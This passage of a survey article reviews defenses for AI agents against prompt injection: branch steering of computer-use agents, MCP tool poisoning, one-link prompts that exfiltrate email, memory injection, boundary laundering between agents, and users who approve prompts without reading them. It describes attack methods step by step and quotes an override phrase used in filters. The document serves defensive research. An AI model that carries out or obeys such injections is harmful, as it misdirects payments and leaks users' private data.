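The possible harm still depends on the plan. In Foerster and colleagues' analysis, one false answer is enough to send the agent to the wrong website or make its task fail. To redirect a payment, the attacker needs a logged-in user whose task already involves a payment. The attacker also needs at least two false answers that agree, such as one for the recipient field and one for the confirmation button. Stealing data requires a plan that both reads something and sends something. Foerster and colleagues demonstrated sending the agent to another website and making it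 click the wrong link, but not stealing data or redirecting a payment.

### Two checks that can also be fooled

Foerster and colleagues tested two defenses that use another model to check the quarantined model's answer. The first compares the answer with the page's underlying structure, which often labels advertisements. The second adds a model from a different company, which examines the screenshot, the original instruction and the answer.

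Each check faced ten attempts at the fake cookie banner attack. The structure check had a recorded detection rate of 6 out of 10 against a simple image advertisement. The second check had a rate of 5 out of 10 against a more flexible type of advertisement, which can supply its own page structure and so hide the label that marks it as an advertisement. These rates may overstate how well the checks work, because Foerster and colleagues attribute some of the failed attacks to plans that happened to look for the cookie button in a different way.

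The checks also raised false alarms. Of 17 ordinary tasks, the structure check flagged four and the combined checks flagged three. All but one of these false alarms involved real cookie banners. In a separate demonstration, small changes to an advertisement's pixels made the quarantined model click the wrong link on a medical website and give a plausible reason for it, and both checks accepted the answer.

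Foerster and colleagues call such checks probabilistic because the checkers are models as well. An image that fools one model often fails to fool a different one, but nothing guarantees this. They also predicted that any data-flow defense for computer-use agents would have to be probabilistic, since a click contains nothing for a policy to check. Nine months later, some of the same researchers published a system that avoids this problem by checking what a click causes.

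### From clicks to network requests

The idea came from ceLLMate, a browser extension by Meng and colleagues. When a click on a website has a lasting effect, the browser normally sends the site an HTTP request, which has a much clearer meaning than the click. For example, a certain request to the code-hosting site GitLab always adds a login key to the user's account, however the agent reached the button.

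The extension has to interpret each request, so every website needs an agent sitemap, a list that matches requests to named actions such as "view cart" or "place order". Meng and colleagues expect website developers to write these lists, as they already write documentation for programmers. Developers or other trusted parties also write policies, such as "allow a purchase up to a maximum amount". A language model that sees no web content selects the policies that suit the user's task, and the user confirms them.

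ceLLMate blocks branch steering towards requests that the policies forbid, because it never relies on the screen to interpret an action. Meng and colleagues state that this neutralises branch steering, but an attacker can still steer the agent between actions that the policies permit. Suppose the user asks an agent to pay an invoice if it is correct and to file a complaint otherwise. The policies have to permit both actions for the whole task, so an attacker can steer the agent from one to the other, or cause a payment at the wrong moment.

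### Constraints for each branch

COBRA, which Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, presented in October 2026, attaches constraints to each branch of the plan. It works as follows:

1. The planner writes a branching program from the user's request and from descriptions of websites and tools that the user has approved.
2. Ordinary code lists the program's actions and branches.
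3. The planner model attaches constraints to each branch, specifying which websites, operations and values it permits. It still has not seen any untrusted data.
4. The interpreter runs the program. The quarantined model reports what is on the screen in a fixed format, such as a price or a date.
5. When the program enters a branch, COBRA activates that branch's constraints in addition to those of any branch around it. It removes them when the program leaves.
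6. Two proxies, which are programs that sit between the agent and the outside world, check every web request and every tool call against the active constraints.

If the active constraints permit a payment of $40, a request to pay $80 fails no matter where the agent clicked. A click on the fake cookie banner would also fail, because the plan doesn't authorise the attacker's website. Like Progent, COBRA has a model write its rules, but COBRA never revises them in response to what the agent reads.

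In the invoice example, COBRA would permit the payment only in the branch for a correct invoice, and only to the authorised recipient for the authorised amount. However, it does not check whether the invoice is correct, so an attacker who deceives the quarantined model about this could still cause the payment. The constraints limit the effects of branch steering but do not prevent it.

### STEER-Bench and the ablations

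Zingrillo and colleagues built a benchmark for these attacks, STEER-Bench, with 101 tasks in nine areas such as bank transfers, warehouse deliveries and medical doses. Testing some tasks in several configurations gives 199 attack cases. CaMeL-NOVA and an undefended agent can run only 74 of these, because neither supports tool calls or approved descriptions. Attacks succeeded in 67 of the 74 cases against the undefended agent (90.5%) and in 65 against CaMeL-NOVA (87.8%). None of the 199 succeeded against COBRA.

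Each of the benchmark's nine suites targets one of COBRA's protections. The researchers ran each suite with the complete system and again with that protection switched off (an ablation). The published percentages imply these counts.

| Protection under test | Successful attacks, complete COBRA | Successful attacks, protection off | Attack success, CaMeL-NOVA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Limits on values in web requests | 0 of 26 | 26 | 96% |
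| Limits on websites and operations | 0 of 24 | 24 | 88% |
| Checks on tool calls | 0 of 15 | 10 | Not tested |
| Same limits for requests and tool calls | 0 of 72 | 72 | 89% |
| Sensitive values only from trusted sources | 0 of 33 | 18 | 100% |
| Detection of altered descriptions | 0 of 5 | 4 | Not tested |
| Separation of planning and execution | 0 of 9 | 6 | 89% |
| Permissions that expire after a branch | 0 of 10 | 10 | 40% |
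| Limits that persist in nested branches | 0 of 5 | 4 | 100% |

174 of the 199 attacks succeeded when the relevant protection was turned off. Another protection blocked the remaining 25. The ablations are good evidence that each part of COBRA stops attacks the others don't.

The comparison with CaMeL-NOVA is less informative than the gap between 87.8% and 0% suggests, because CaMeL-NOVA deliberately leaves out CaMeL's data-flow policies and COBRA's designers chose the attacks to match COBRA's protections. In the cases on separating planning from execution, the attacker tries to add an action to the plan. A fixed plan should prevent this, yet CaMeL-NOVA failed in 89% of these cases. This is probably because STEER-Bench counts harmful outcomes, and a click that was already in the plan can produce one.

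COBRA kept 97% of benign utility on STEER-Bench. It blocked legitimate actions in four of 138 cases without an attack. All four involved permissions that changed between branches or combined in nested ones. The 97% excludes tasks in which COBRA was right to stop and ask the user a question.

OSWorld-MCP, a broader benchmark, gives a better idea of how much the defense reduces performance. Each agent had up to five attempts at each of 361 tasks, and COBRA's only restriction on web requests was which websites they could go to.

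| Models | Solved by an ordinary agent | Solved with COBRA |
|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS, with GPT-5 as COBRA's planner | 85 (23.5%) | 133 (36.8%) |
| Kimi K2.5 in both roles | 152 (42.1%) | 92 (25.5%) |
| Claude Sonnet 5 in both roles | 184 (51.0%) | 140 (38.8%) |

The first row shows a gain, but that setup also adds a much stronger model. When the same model does all the work, planning blind loses between an eighth and a sixth of all tasks. COBRA can recover some of these by writing five plans and merging them into one program with more fallbacks, which raised the number of tasks solved on the first attempt from 78 to 105.

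### Who writes the constraints

COBRA's proxies are ordinary code, but a language model generates the constraints they enforce. Zingrillo and colleagues audited 30 STEER-Bench cases by writing down the correct constraints before running COBRA, then testing whether the generated ones allowed and blocked the right operations. The generated constraints were right in 28 cases. In one case they blocked an operation the user had authorised, and in another they allowed one the user had not authorised.

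One permissive error in a sample of 30 is statistically consistent with a true rate as high as 17%. COBRA still blocked every attack in the benchmark, apparently because none of them exploited this error. The planner model wrote these constraints without interference from an attacker, so isolating it more strictly would not have prevented the error.

### Who describes the website

COBRA needs an approved sitemap to permit one operation on a website while forbidding another. Without one, its constraints can only allow or block the whole site.

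Zingrillo and colleagues tested COBRA on 21 attacks from WASP, a benchmark of prompt injections against web agents. Without sitemaps, COBRA blocked the five attacks that sent requests to another website, but the 14 that misused the site the agent was already on all succeeded. In one of these, the user wanted to comment on a GitLab issue, and the injection made the agent add an access key to a code repository on the same site instead. With sitemaps, COBRA blocked all 19 of these attacks and still completed every legitimate task. The other two attacks depended on the meaning of free text in a permitted request, which COBRA does not check.

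Few websites publish sitemaps, so Zingrillo and colleagues built MESA, which explores a website and has a model draft a sitemap. The drafts contained every necessary operation for 18 of 25 website tasks in OSWorld-MCP. With the drafts, COBRA still completed 10 of the 11 tasks in this group that it had completed without them.

Drafting a sitemap this way gives attackers a new opening. Piet and colleagues warn that a model exploring a website reads reviews, comments and advertisements, and that instructions hidden there could corrupt the description it writes. A function that supposedly only fetches reviews might also send data to an attacker, and this would affect every later task. MESA's prompts mark website content as data, which is the kind of in-band defense these systems were supposed to make unnecessary. The remaining protection is review by the website's owner, who is supposed to correct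 the draft, and by the user, who has to approve the final version, including its free-text descriptions. COBRA then stores a digital fingerprint of the approved file and asks for approval again if the file changes. This detects later tampering but not mistakes the user has already approved.

Some owners may have little reason to help. Zingrillo and colleagues note that owners whose websites earn money from advertising want human visitors, and may not want to make their sites' operations easier for agents to use.

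### Replacing clicks with named operations

If someone has to describe every operation on a website, the agent could call those operations directly instead of clicking. Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026) built an agent called Baya on this principle in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*. They wrote interfaces by hand for four simulated websites. Where a site had no suitable operation, they wrote a named, fixed browser script. One forum's own interface covered only a third of its tasks and had no operation for posting a reply.

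Baya's planner writes a Python program with these operations before the agent visits the site. Baya solved 77.8% of 581 tasks, averaged over three models. An ordinary agent solved 66.7% with the same interfaces and a browser, and 55.1% with only a browser. Baya took over five minutes per task, compared with about one and a half for the ordinary agent with the interfaces.

No WASP attack influenced Baya's actions. The attacks influenced the two ordinary agents in 16.2% and 25.5% of cases, though they rarely achieved their final goal. These tests used injected instructions. Chow and colleagues' threat model excludes attacks that only change the result of a task, such as which product the agent buys, so it leaves out much of branch steering. But Baya gives such attacks fewer opportunities because its programs mostly sort and filter data with ordinary code. In 98.2% of runs, no model read any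 website content.

Baya also depends on its interfaces when a program fails. The planner receives the error message and writes a new program, up to three times. As in CaMeL's retry loop, an error message could carry an attacker's text to the planner, so Chow and colleagues require that no trusted operation repeat website text in its errors.

### Tool descriptions and dishonest servers

Computer-use agents increasingly combine clicking with tools from outside companies. Many of these tools use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024. When an agent connects to an MCP server, the server sends the names and descriptions of its tools, and the agent's software passes them to the model. In a dual-model system, that model is the planner, which can't plan without them. An attacker who runs a server can therefore send text to the one model that is supposed to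 be isolated.

This attack is called tool poisoning. *MCPTox* (Wang, Gao et al., 2025) distinguishes three forms. In the first, the description of a tool that supposedly tells the time may tell the agent to read a private key first. In the second, the description of a supposed security check may tell the agent to read the key before any file operation. In the third, the description tells the agent to change the arguments of other tools, such as the recipient of every email. The attacker's tool never has to run, because the agent does the damage with legitimate tools.

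Wang and colleagues wrote 1,348 such cases for 45 real servers and tested 20 model configurations. The attacks succeeded 36.5% of the time on average and 72.8% with o1-mini, an OpenAI model from 2024. No model explicitly refused in more than 3% of cases. Those models are old, so the rates are weak evidence about current ones, but planners still have to read tool descriptions.

COBRA's planner reads a tool's description only if the user has approved it. As with sitemaps, COBRA blocks a tool whose description has changed since approval. It also confirms that each call reaches the approved server, in case another server offers a tool with the same name. But if the user approves a poisoned description, the text reaches both the planner and the step that writes the constraints, so the constraints could permit the attack.

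Zingrillo and colleagues tested the checks on tool calls with 1,223 MCPTox cases. In 1,210 of them, the attack changed which tool the agent called or the arguments it used. COBRA blocked all of these attacks, and without the checks they all succeeded. That success rate is far higher than Wang and colleagues found with real models, so the test seems to show what the checks do once a model has obeyed the attacker. COBRA completed 79% of the legitimate tasks under attack, compared with 100% without enforcement, and the drop was mainly due to poor plans.

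COBRA could not detect the other 13 attacks, in which the agent made exactly the call the user wanted and the server did something harmful with it. For example, a dishonest server could save a note as requested and also send a copy to someone else. An honest server would receive the same call, so no check on the agent's side can tell the two servers apart.

### What a request leaves out

Some important facts appear only on the screen. A shop's checkout request may list the items but not the total price. COBRA then has to rely on the quarantined model to read the price, which might read a number in an advertisement instead. Zingrillo and colleagues acknowledge that COBRA can't enforce a spending limit in this case. ceLLMate partly solves this problem by letting its sitemap specify which page element contains the total, which ordinary code then reads. This works as long as the developer keeps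 the sitemap up to date and an attacker can't alter that element.

Other actions never pass through the proxies. An email program can send messages through SMTP, and a desktop program can write directly to the disk. In tests on OS-Harm, a benchmark of harmful computer tasks, 30 of 51 attacks used channels that COBRA's web proxy does not inspect. COBRA still stopped them because the plan didn't include those actions, and CaMeL-NOVA stopped them too. If the user's task involved sending mail through such a program, COBRA would have no deterministic check on the recipient.

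COBRA also doesn't count operations. A plan might try to pay with a tool and then fall back to the website if the tool doesn't respond. If the first payment went through and only the confirmation was lost, the agent could pay again on the website, and both payments would satisfy the constraints. The researchers did not test this. ceLLMate's designers noticed that a $50 limit on one purchase does not stop two purchases of $49, so ceLLMate can also limit how many times the agent makes a certain request.

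### Asking for what the request left out

When a task needs a sensitive value that no trusted source supplies, COBRA's planner asks the user before the program runs. It is also supposed to ask if the user's permission depends on a fact that only untrusted content can establish, such as whether an invoice is correct. COBRA asks only during planning, so untrusted content can't trigger a question.

The planner asked a clarifying question in 20 of 22 cases where the request was missing something important, and asked no unnecessary questions in 11 cases where the request was complete. For example, when a user wanted an order sent to "the saved delivery address", COBRA asked for the address because an attacker might have changed the saved one.

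In a follow-up test on 11 tasks, a simulated user answered COBRA's question. When the user supplied the missing value and there was no attack, COBRA completed 10 tasks. When the user gave permission to use the saved record, COBRA stopped safely every time without completing the task. No attack succeeded with either answer. The user therefore has to know the value and type it in, and can't just tell the agent to trust the file. The test covered only missing values, so it doesn't show whether COBRA handles doubtful facts, such as whether an invoice is correct.

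To send Bob the document, COBRA should ask the user for Bob's address before it opens the meeting notes. If the user knows the address, the document goes to Bob. But if the user types in the address from the notes, which the attacker has altered, COBRA treats the attacker's address as trusted.

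## Requests, memory and messages from other agents that are assumed to be trusted

COBRA treats the user's request as trusted, as do other systems including CaMeL, FIDES and Progent. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026), a design for coding agents, also lists the request among its trusted inputs.

The system labels text "trusted" based on how it arrived, regardless of who wrote it. The user may have pasted it from elsewhere, a link may have prefilled it, the agent may have saved it in an earlier session, or another agent may have sent it. If an attacker wrote it, the planner turns it into a plan, and the rest of the system protects that plan from interference.

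### Pasted text

Suppose a user pastes an email that asks for a payment to a new account into the request and adds "please deal with this". CaMeL's planner reads the email and writes a program that pays that account. The account number is a constant in the program, so the interpreter treats it as trusted and the payment policy allows the call. If the assistant had fetched the same email from the inbox, the account number would have been untrusted and the policy would have blocked the payment.

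*AgentSecBench* (2026), a benchmark for prompt injection, counts the user's request as trusted and any text copied from external systems as untrusted. An email pasted into the request fits both descriptions, and the planner receives a single string with no marker separating the user's words from the email.

Tallam and Miller suggest a partial remedy for uploaded files. The system would tag every value extracted from them, and policies would keep those values out of irreversible actions unless someone granted an exception. This is feasible because the software can detect uploads. For pasted text, it would have to detect the paste or offer a separate box. *Sleeper Channels and Provenance Gates* (2026), a design for agents that run continuously, includes the clipboard among the inputs whose origin the system must track. But people also paste instructions they want the agent to follow, so knowing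 that text came from the clipboard does not establish whether the user wants the agent to obey it.

### Prompts filled in by a link

Many assistants accept a prompt inside a web address, so clicking such a link opens the assistant with the prompt already in the input box. Microsoft (2026) reviewed these links in email traffic over 60 days. It found 50 distinct prompts from 31 companies that tried to store a promotional message in the assistant's long-term memory. The companies were real businesses, including a security vendor, and they hid the prompts behind "Summarize with AI" buttons or share links. A typical prompt asked for a summary of a page and then told the assistant to remember the company as a trusted source.

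These figures are for attempts, and Microsoft does not report how many of them changed an assistant's memory. It found that the attempts' effectiveness varied between assistants and over time, and that some behaviours reported earlier no longer occurred.

Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) documents a more serious flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Personal. A crafted link could make the assistant run a prompt as soon as the page opened, before the user pressed anything. Copilot processed the prompt as if the user had typed it. In Varonis' tests, it searched a connected email account and sent what it found to an outside server. Varonis reported the flaw in December 2025, and Microsoft shipped patches in August 2026. There was no evidence that attackers had used it. Mascellino (2026), in *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant*, reports a similar one-link flaw in Atlassian's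 assistant, which has since been fixed.

Isolating the planner from tool results would not have stopped this attack, because the attacker's text arrived as the request. Confidentiality rules would have helped more, because they depend on the emails' labels. FIDES's second basic policy would block sending private email to an outside server, whoever asked for it. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* makes this protection an explicit goal, and its threat model includes a hostile user prompt. But confidentiality rules can't stop a hostile request to delete a file or pay the wrong person, because neither action has to reveal a secret.

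The application can detect when a link has supplied the text, so it can at least avoid running the prompt automatically. If it waits for the user to press Enter, doing so counts as endorsing the text, even if the user hasn't read it.

### Screening the request

Tallam and Miller propose a gateway that examines the request before the planner does. It would check the reputation of any web addresses, look for phrases such as "ignore all previous", and measure how statistically unusual the text is. They report that the checks took less than five milliseconds in internal tests, but they give no detection rate or false-alarm rate.

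The prompts that Microsoft collected would probably pass all three checks. Most link to legitimate businesses' websites, and they use ordinary English with no override phrase. Microsoft recommends searching for links that contain words such as "remember" and "trusted source". These words match the prompts it found, but an attacker can use others, and a user who wants the assistant to remember a preference may use the same ones. Tallam and Miller call keyword filters brittle and cite studies in which such filters blocked fewer than 30% of new jailbreak strategies.

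A language model would handle rewording better, but an attacker can fool it. Nasr and colleagues' adaptive attacks defeated most of the defenses they tested, including filters. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) calls this kind of inspection an arms race that "guarantees nothing".

A filter can still be useful if it can only lower trust. By rejecting requests that the system would otherwise have accepted, it may stop an attack, though it will also block some legitimate requests. But if the system trusts a link's text because the filter didn't flag it, the guarantees of the planner, the labels and the policies all depend on a fallible model having classified that text correctly.

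### From one CaMeL agent to another

In some multi-agent systems, an orchestrator receives the user's request and calls specialised agents as tools. Those agents treat the orchestrator as their user. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* tests whether such a system is secure if every agent runs CaMeL.

The researchers built an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent that could send email and Slack messages. The user asked for a summary of all job applicants' information to go to Julie on Slack. An attacker had stored an instruction in the database to send the same information to an outside email address. The attack worked as follows:

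1. The orchestrator's planner wrote a program to fetch the applicants' details, summarise them and pass the summary to the notification agent.
2. The database agent ran its query. The result, including the injection, stayed in a variable that its planner never saw.
3. The orchestrator's quarantined model summarised the result, and the injection survived in the summary. The orchestrator's planner did not see this either.
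4. The orchestrator's program inserted the summary into a sentence and sent it on: `notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")`.
5. The notification agent received that sentence as its user's request. Its planner read the injection and wrote a program that messaged Julie and also emailed the outsider.

The first two agents ran the same programs as they did without the attack. Each agent followed a plan based on what it took to be its user's request, so each had control-flow integrity, but the whole system did not. The researchers call this boundary laundering because untrusted data becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to the next.

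Protecting each agent separately does stop some attacks. In another test, an attacker used public data to try to make a database agent open a private database. That attack has to hijack the agent that reads the data, and it failed in all five trials.

The paper also proves that in any system with at least two agents, arranged as a tree, and at least one tool that returns untrusted data, there is some user request for which untrusted data determines an agent's plan. The proof assumes that a user can ask any agent to call a tool and return the result, or to use one tool's result in a call to another. If the agent with the untrusted tool has a child, it can put the tool's result into the child's instructions. If it has only a parent, it can return the result, and the parent can put it into a second request to the same agent. The theorem doesn't show how often users would make such a request.

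### Two channels between agents

The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each call to another agent into two parts:

```
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary provided to Julie via Slack",
    variables={"summary": summary},
)
```

The child's planner reads only `message`. Its program can fetch the summary from `variables` when it runs, as it would fetch a tool's result. The interpreter ensures that `message` does not depend on any tool's output, which gives the whole system control-flow integrity. It also keeps the tags on values in `variables` when they reach the child, which lets policies work across agents. For example, the summary is still tagged as coming from a database when it reaches the notification agent.

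The first rule relies on the interpreter to track every dependency, so CaMeL's tracking errors matter even more here. If a formatted string still lost its untrusted tag, the orchestrator's original sentence would pass the check on `message`.

To test the design, the researchers adapted AgentDojo by dividing each suite's tools among two to four agents under an orchestrator. This gave 97 user tasks and 949 attacked cases for each of five models. The task counts below come from runs without an attack.

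| Model | Attack success: no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL | Tasks solved: no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% | 67 | 52 | 51 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% | 84 | 71 | 64 |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% | 76 | 37 | 24 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% | 74 | 41 | 26 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% | 27 | 13 | 7 |

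Running CaMeL in each agent had already stopped nearly all the attacks. The percentages imply that nine attacks succeeded in 4,745 cases. All nine were boundary laundering, and multi-CaMeL stopped them too. As with other AgentDojo results, the attacks were fixed texts. An attacker who knew that one agent's output became another's request could target that boundary, so the count of nine is probably a poor guide to the risk.

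The paper describes the drop in performance as modest for the strongest models. That fits Fable 5, which refused 52 of the harmless tasks but solved 84% of the rest with multi-CaMeL, compared with 91% without a defense. GPT-5.5 lost more, falling from 84 solved tasks to 64, or about 21 percentage points, though it lost only eight points on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks. Most failures came from committing to a plan too early. Sometimes an agent that could not find the requested data returned data for a different machine or period, and the orchestrator's program continued unchanged.

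All these tests ran without data-flow policies, and one published run shows the risk. The user asked Multi-CaMeL to invite Dora to Slack and send her feedback on her website, where an attacker had planted an injection. Multi-CaMeL ignored the injection but invited Dora using an email address it had extracted from the same page, so an attacker could have supplied a different address, as in the example of Bob's document. The planner also wrote the feedback, which praised the site's "clean design", before any agent had opened the page.

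### Memory that keeps its labels

An agent with a memory can also send untrusted text to itself. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and keep its details, and on Tuesday to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the invoice contains an injection, the planner might read the injection on Tuesday. Even if the planner never reads it, the payment could go to an attacker's account number stored with the invoice.

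SPA writes and checks a complete plan for each request before any tool runs. After a successful run, it saves every value that a tool or the quarantined model produced, in three parts:

- The value itself, which no planner sees.
- Its label, with separate entries for secrecy and trust.
- A description of what the value represents, its format and the request that produced it.

Tuesday's planner receives only the description of the stored value. Monday's planner wrote that description before the agent opened the invoice, so the invoice could not influence it. To use the value itself, the plan must include an explicit step to retrieve it, which restores the value's original label.

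SPA combines labels in the usual way. With *C* for secrecy level and *I* for trust level, data may flow from a source *s* to a destination *d* only if:

*C*(*s*) ⊑ *C*(*d*) and *I*(*d*) ⊑ *I*(*s*).

Data can move from a source to a destination only if the destination is cleared for data that secret and the source is as trusted as the destination requires. The retrieved invoice is untrusted, and so is the account number that the quarantined model extracts from it. If the payment tool requires trusted input, SPA rejects the plan before it starts, even if the invoice is genuine.

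SPA's small planning language also closes two of CaMeL's leaks. A variable created inside a branch disappears when the branch ends, so a program can't use CaMeL's two-flag trick. A rejected plan ends the request, so there is no retry loop. Girrens and Wang define the rules precisely but do not present a noninterference theorem.

The evaluation of SPA used GPT-5.4-nano on AgentDojo and on a version of it that splits each of the 97 tasks into two to five successive requests. Each setting had 949 attacked runs.

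| Version of SPA | Tasks solved, single request | Attack success | Tasks solved, several requests | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Label checks on | 29.0% | 0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |
| Label checks off | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Label checks off, planner sees stored values | Not tested | Not tested | 65.9% | 0.6% |

The 0.2% corresponds to two runs. Girrens and Wang describe two runs in which AgentDojo recorded a success even though SPA had already rejected the plan, so these were probably scoring errors.

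The last row matters most for judging the memory design. It reports results with the main protection removed, so that later planners see stored values, yet the attack success rate rises by only 0.3 percentage points, or about three runs. Because the attack rarely works even without the protection, this test can't show that the protection works. Girrens and Wang acknowledge this and say that future tests need attacks designed to lie dormant in memory.

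The results show that an agent can reuse stored values without its planner reading them. With label checks on, later plans retrieved the right stored result in 89.9% of the cases where one existed. But the checks also stopped about 45% of runs in the test with several requests. SPA applies one trust requirement to all of a tool's inputs, so it can't accept an untrusted subject line while requiring a trusted recipient. Girrens and Wang suggest recovering some of the lost tasks by setting a separate requirement for each input and allowing limited forms of endorsement.

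SPA assumes that every request is trusted and that whoever deploys it has set the labels and policies correctly. If the first assumption fails, the effect lasts longer than in a system without memory, because SPA's planner also receives a record of earlier requests in the session. If an attacker's link had filled in one request, the planner would receive the attacker's text again with every later request in that session.

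### Labels that both sides honour

A label is a record that one system keeps about a value, so another system that receives the value as plain text doesn't get the label. Multi-CaMeL avoids this because the parent and the child run the same interpreter. The parent sends the labels with the values, and the child keeps the labeled values away from its planner and checks them against its policies. If the child pasted everything in `variables` into its planner's prompt, the labels would not protect the planner from instructions injected in those values.

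Relying on a sender's trust labels is harder when different organisations run the two agents. They may define "trusted" differently, and the receiver can't verify that the sender tracked its data properly. A cautious receiver would give a message the lower of two trust levels, the one the sender claims and the one the receiver assigns to the sender. An unknown company's agent could then label its message untrusted, but labelling it trusted would have no effect.

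Labels are easy to lose even within one system, because models paraphrase and combine what they read. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) reports that current defenses usually check a memory only when the agent writes it, and recommends expiry dates, version histories and a way to undo changes. In the design from *Sleeper Channels and Provenance Gates*, a summary inherits the origins of everything it summarises, and new permissions can come only through a separate, hardware-backed channel that the model can't write to.

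When a label is missing, the system has no record of where the data came from or who may see it. It is safest to treat the data as both untrusted and secret, but most of the rules for unlabelled data in Microsoft's framework treat it as public. The system should also record that the label was missing, so that the default isn't mistaken for a label someone assigned. Developers could then find the tools that cause the most unnecessary refusals and label them properly, without relaxing the default for everything else.

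## User approval as the last check

A policy based on where data came from treats a genuine meeting request and a forged one alike, so it has to refuse both, allow both or ask the user. CaMeL, RTBAS and the released version of FIDES can all ask, so their security partly depends on how users answer.

### Tasks that need untrusted data

In the calendar task that Costa and colleagues describe, an agent creates an event if one of the user's emails requests a meeting. A strict policy blocks the event because its date and guests come from an untrusted email.

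Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, describe a user who asks an agent to look up a recipe for lamingtons and buy any special ingredients. The user wants the recipe website to determine the shopping list, so a rule that kept untrusted data out of the order would make the task impossible.

Tasks like these could produce many approval prompts. When Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL without any attacks, its policies blocked 26 of 97 AgentDojo tasks. If CaMeL had asked the user instead, approval would have been the right answer in all 26 cases. At that rate, a thousand ordinary tasks would produce at least 268 prompts. If an attack added one more, a user who approved everything without reading would be right 268 times out of 269.

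Narisetty and colleagues propose that tests of these defenses also record how often the system asks for endorsement. This would measure both the burden on the user and how much the security depends on human judgment that an attacker can target.

### What one approval permits

| System | When it asks | What the user can see | What one approval permits |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | A policy denies a call, such as an email to an unknown address | The message and its recipient | That message |
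| RTBAS | The labels of the data behind a call break the tool's rule | The call and the kinds of private data it would release | That call |
| FIDES, as released | The conversation's label breaks the tool's rule | The tool and the label that caused the refusal | That call |

In RTBAS and FIDES, approving a call does not make the data behind it trusted. RTBAS gives the call's result the restrictive label that triggered the approval request, and a FIDES conversation stays untrusted after the user approves a call. A mistaken approval therefore permits only one action, but the user may have to answer a similar question soon after.

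RTBAS is designed to ask the user less often by estimating which parts of the conversation matter for the next call. It combines the labels of those parts and hides from the agent anything more secret or less trusted than the combined label. If that label breaks the tool's rule, the system waits for the user's approval, and if the user declines, the agent skips the call and continues. Because the agent can't see the hidden parts, Zhong and colleagues argue that a wrong estimate causes extra prompts or missing information but no breach. However, the component that makes the estimate must read the untrusted text.

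Zhong and colleagues did not test how people respond to these prompts. In their AgentDojo test, RTBAS skipped every call that needed approval, as if the user had refused each request. It stopped all attacks that violated its policies, but solved only 22% or 33% of the Slack tasks, depending on the version of RTBAS. Many of those tasks require acting on untrusted websites. A real user would approve some requests, which would recover lost tasks but could also let attacks through.

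The second test of RTBAS used 37 cases involving private data. Asking the user to approve every tool call led to unnecessary requests in 11 cases, compared with three and six for the two versions of RTBAS. Each version failed to make a necessary request in four cases.

RTBAS can also show which kinds of private data a call would release. This could help a user who is willing to share a card number to book a flight, but not a social security number. One version identified exactly the right kinds for about 70% of calls. The other did so for 57%, and listing every kind of private data in the conversation did almost as well (56.7%).

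### Permission prompts in Claude Code

The best evidence on how people answer approval requests comes from coding agents. Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, reviewed 21 production systems and found that 15 ask for approval while the agent works. These systems usually ask based on the type of action, whereas CaMeL, RTBAS and FIDES ask based on where data came from or who may see it.

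Claude Code originally let the agent read files freely but asked before it changed a file, ran a shell command or used the network. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that users approved about 93% of these prompts. Approval fatigue, in which people pay less attention to each request as they see more of them, appeared within weeks. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a later rate of 97%, with developers making "dozens or hundreds" of these decisions every day.

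Most commands are harmless, so a perfect reviewer might approve even more than 97% of them, and a high approval rate does not by itself show carelessness. But many users turn the prompts off. By June 2026, 62% had either used the mode that skips permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions started in that mode. Nearly half of the users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run automatically. Many of these rules allow any Python or Node program, and so in practice allow almost anything.

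Experienced users approve everything automatically roughly twice as often as new users, who do so in about 20% of sessions, according to Anthropic findings reported in The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else*. Anthropic also found that experienced users interrupt the agent more. Interrupting can stop an agent that is drifting from its task, but it may come too late to prevent a payment or a password leak.

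*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) reports a survey of 203 developers who use coding agents. 64% said they often approve at least one type of action without close review, as did 61% of those who carefully review most or all of the code their agents write. Developers who knew of security or privacy problems with agents were more likely to do this (70%) than those who did not (43%), and the difference remained after the researchers adjusted for how much people used agents. These are self-reports from volunteers, but they give little support to the idea that warning people about attacks makes them read approval prompts more carefully.

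Reading an approval prompt may not help if it shows only a command. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents harming files and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports, the user had turned on automatic approval. In 31, the prompt didn't give the user enough information to judge the action. For example, `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it permits whatever the script contains.

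### A planted dangerous command

Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor to measure whether people notice a harmful request. The testers knew only that they were in a coding study. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Approving it had no effect, but the vendor recorded the answer.

The command was refused by 143 testers (13.6%). The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic also ran the commands through auto mode, in which a language model decides whether an action may proceed. The model blocked 937 of them (89%), including 800 that testers had approved, but allowed six that testers had refused. Testers and the model both allowed 110.

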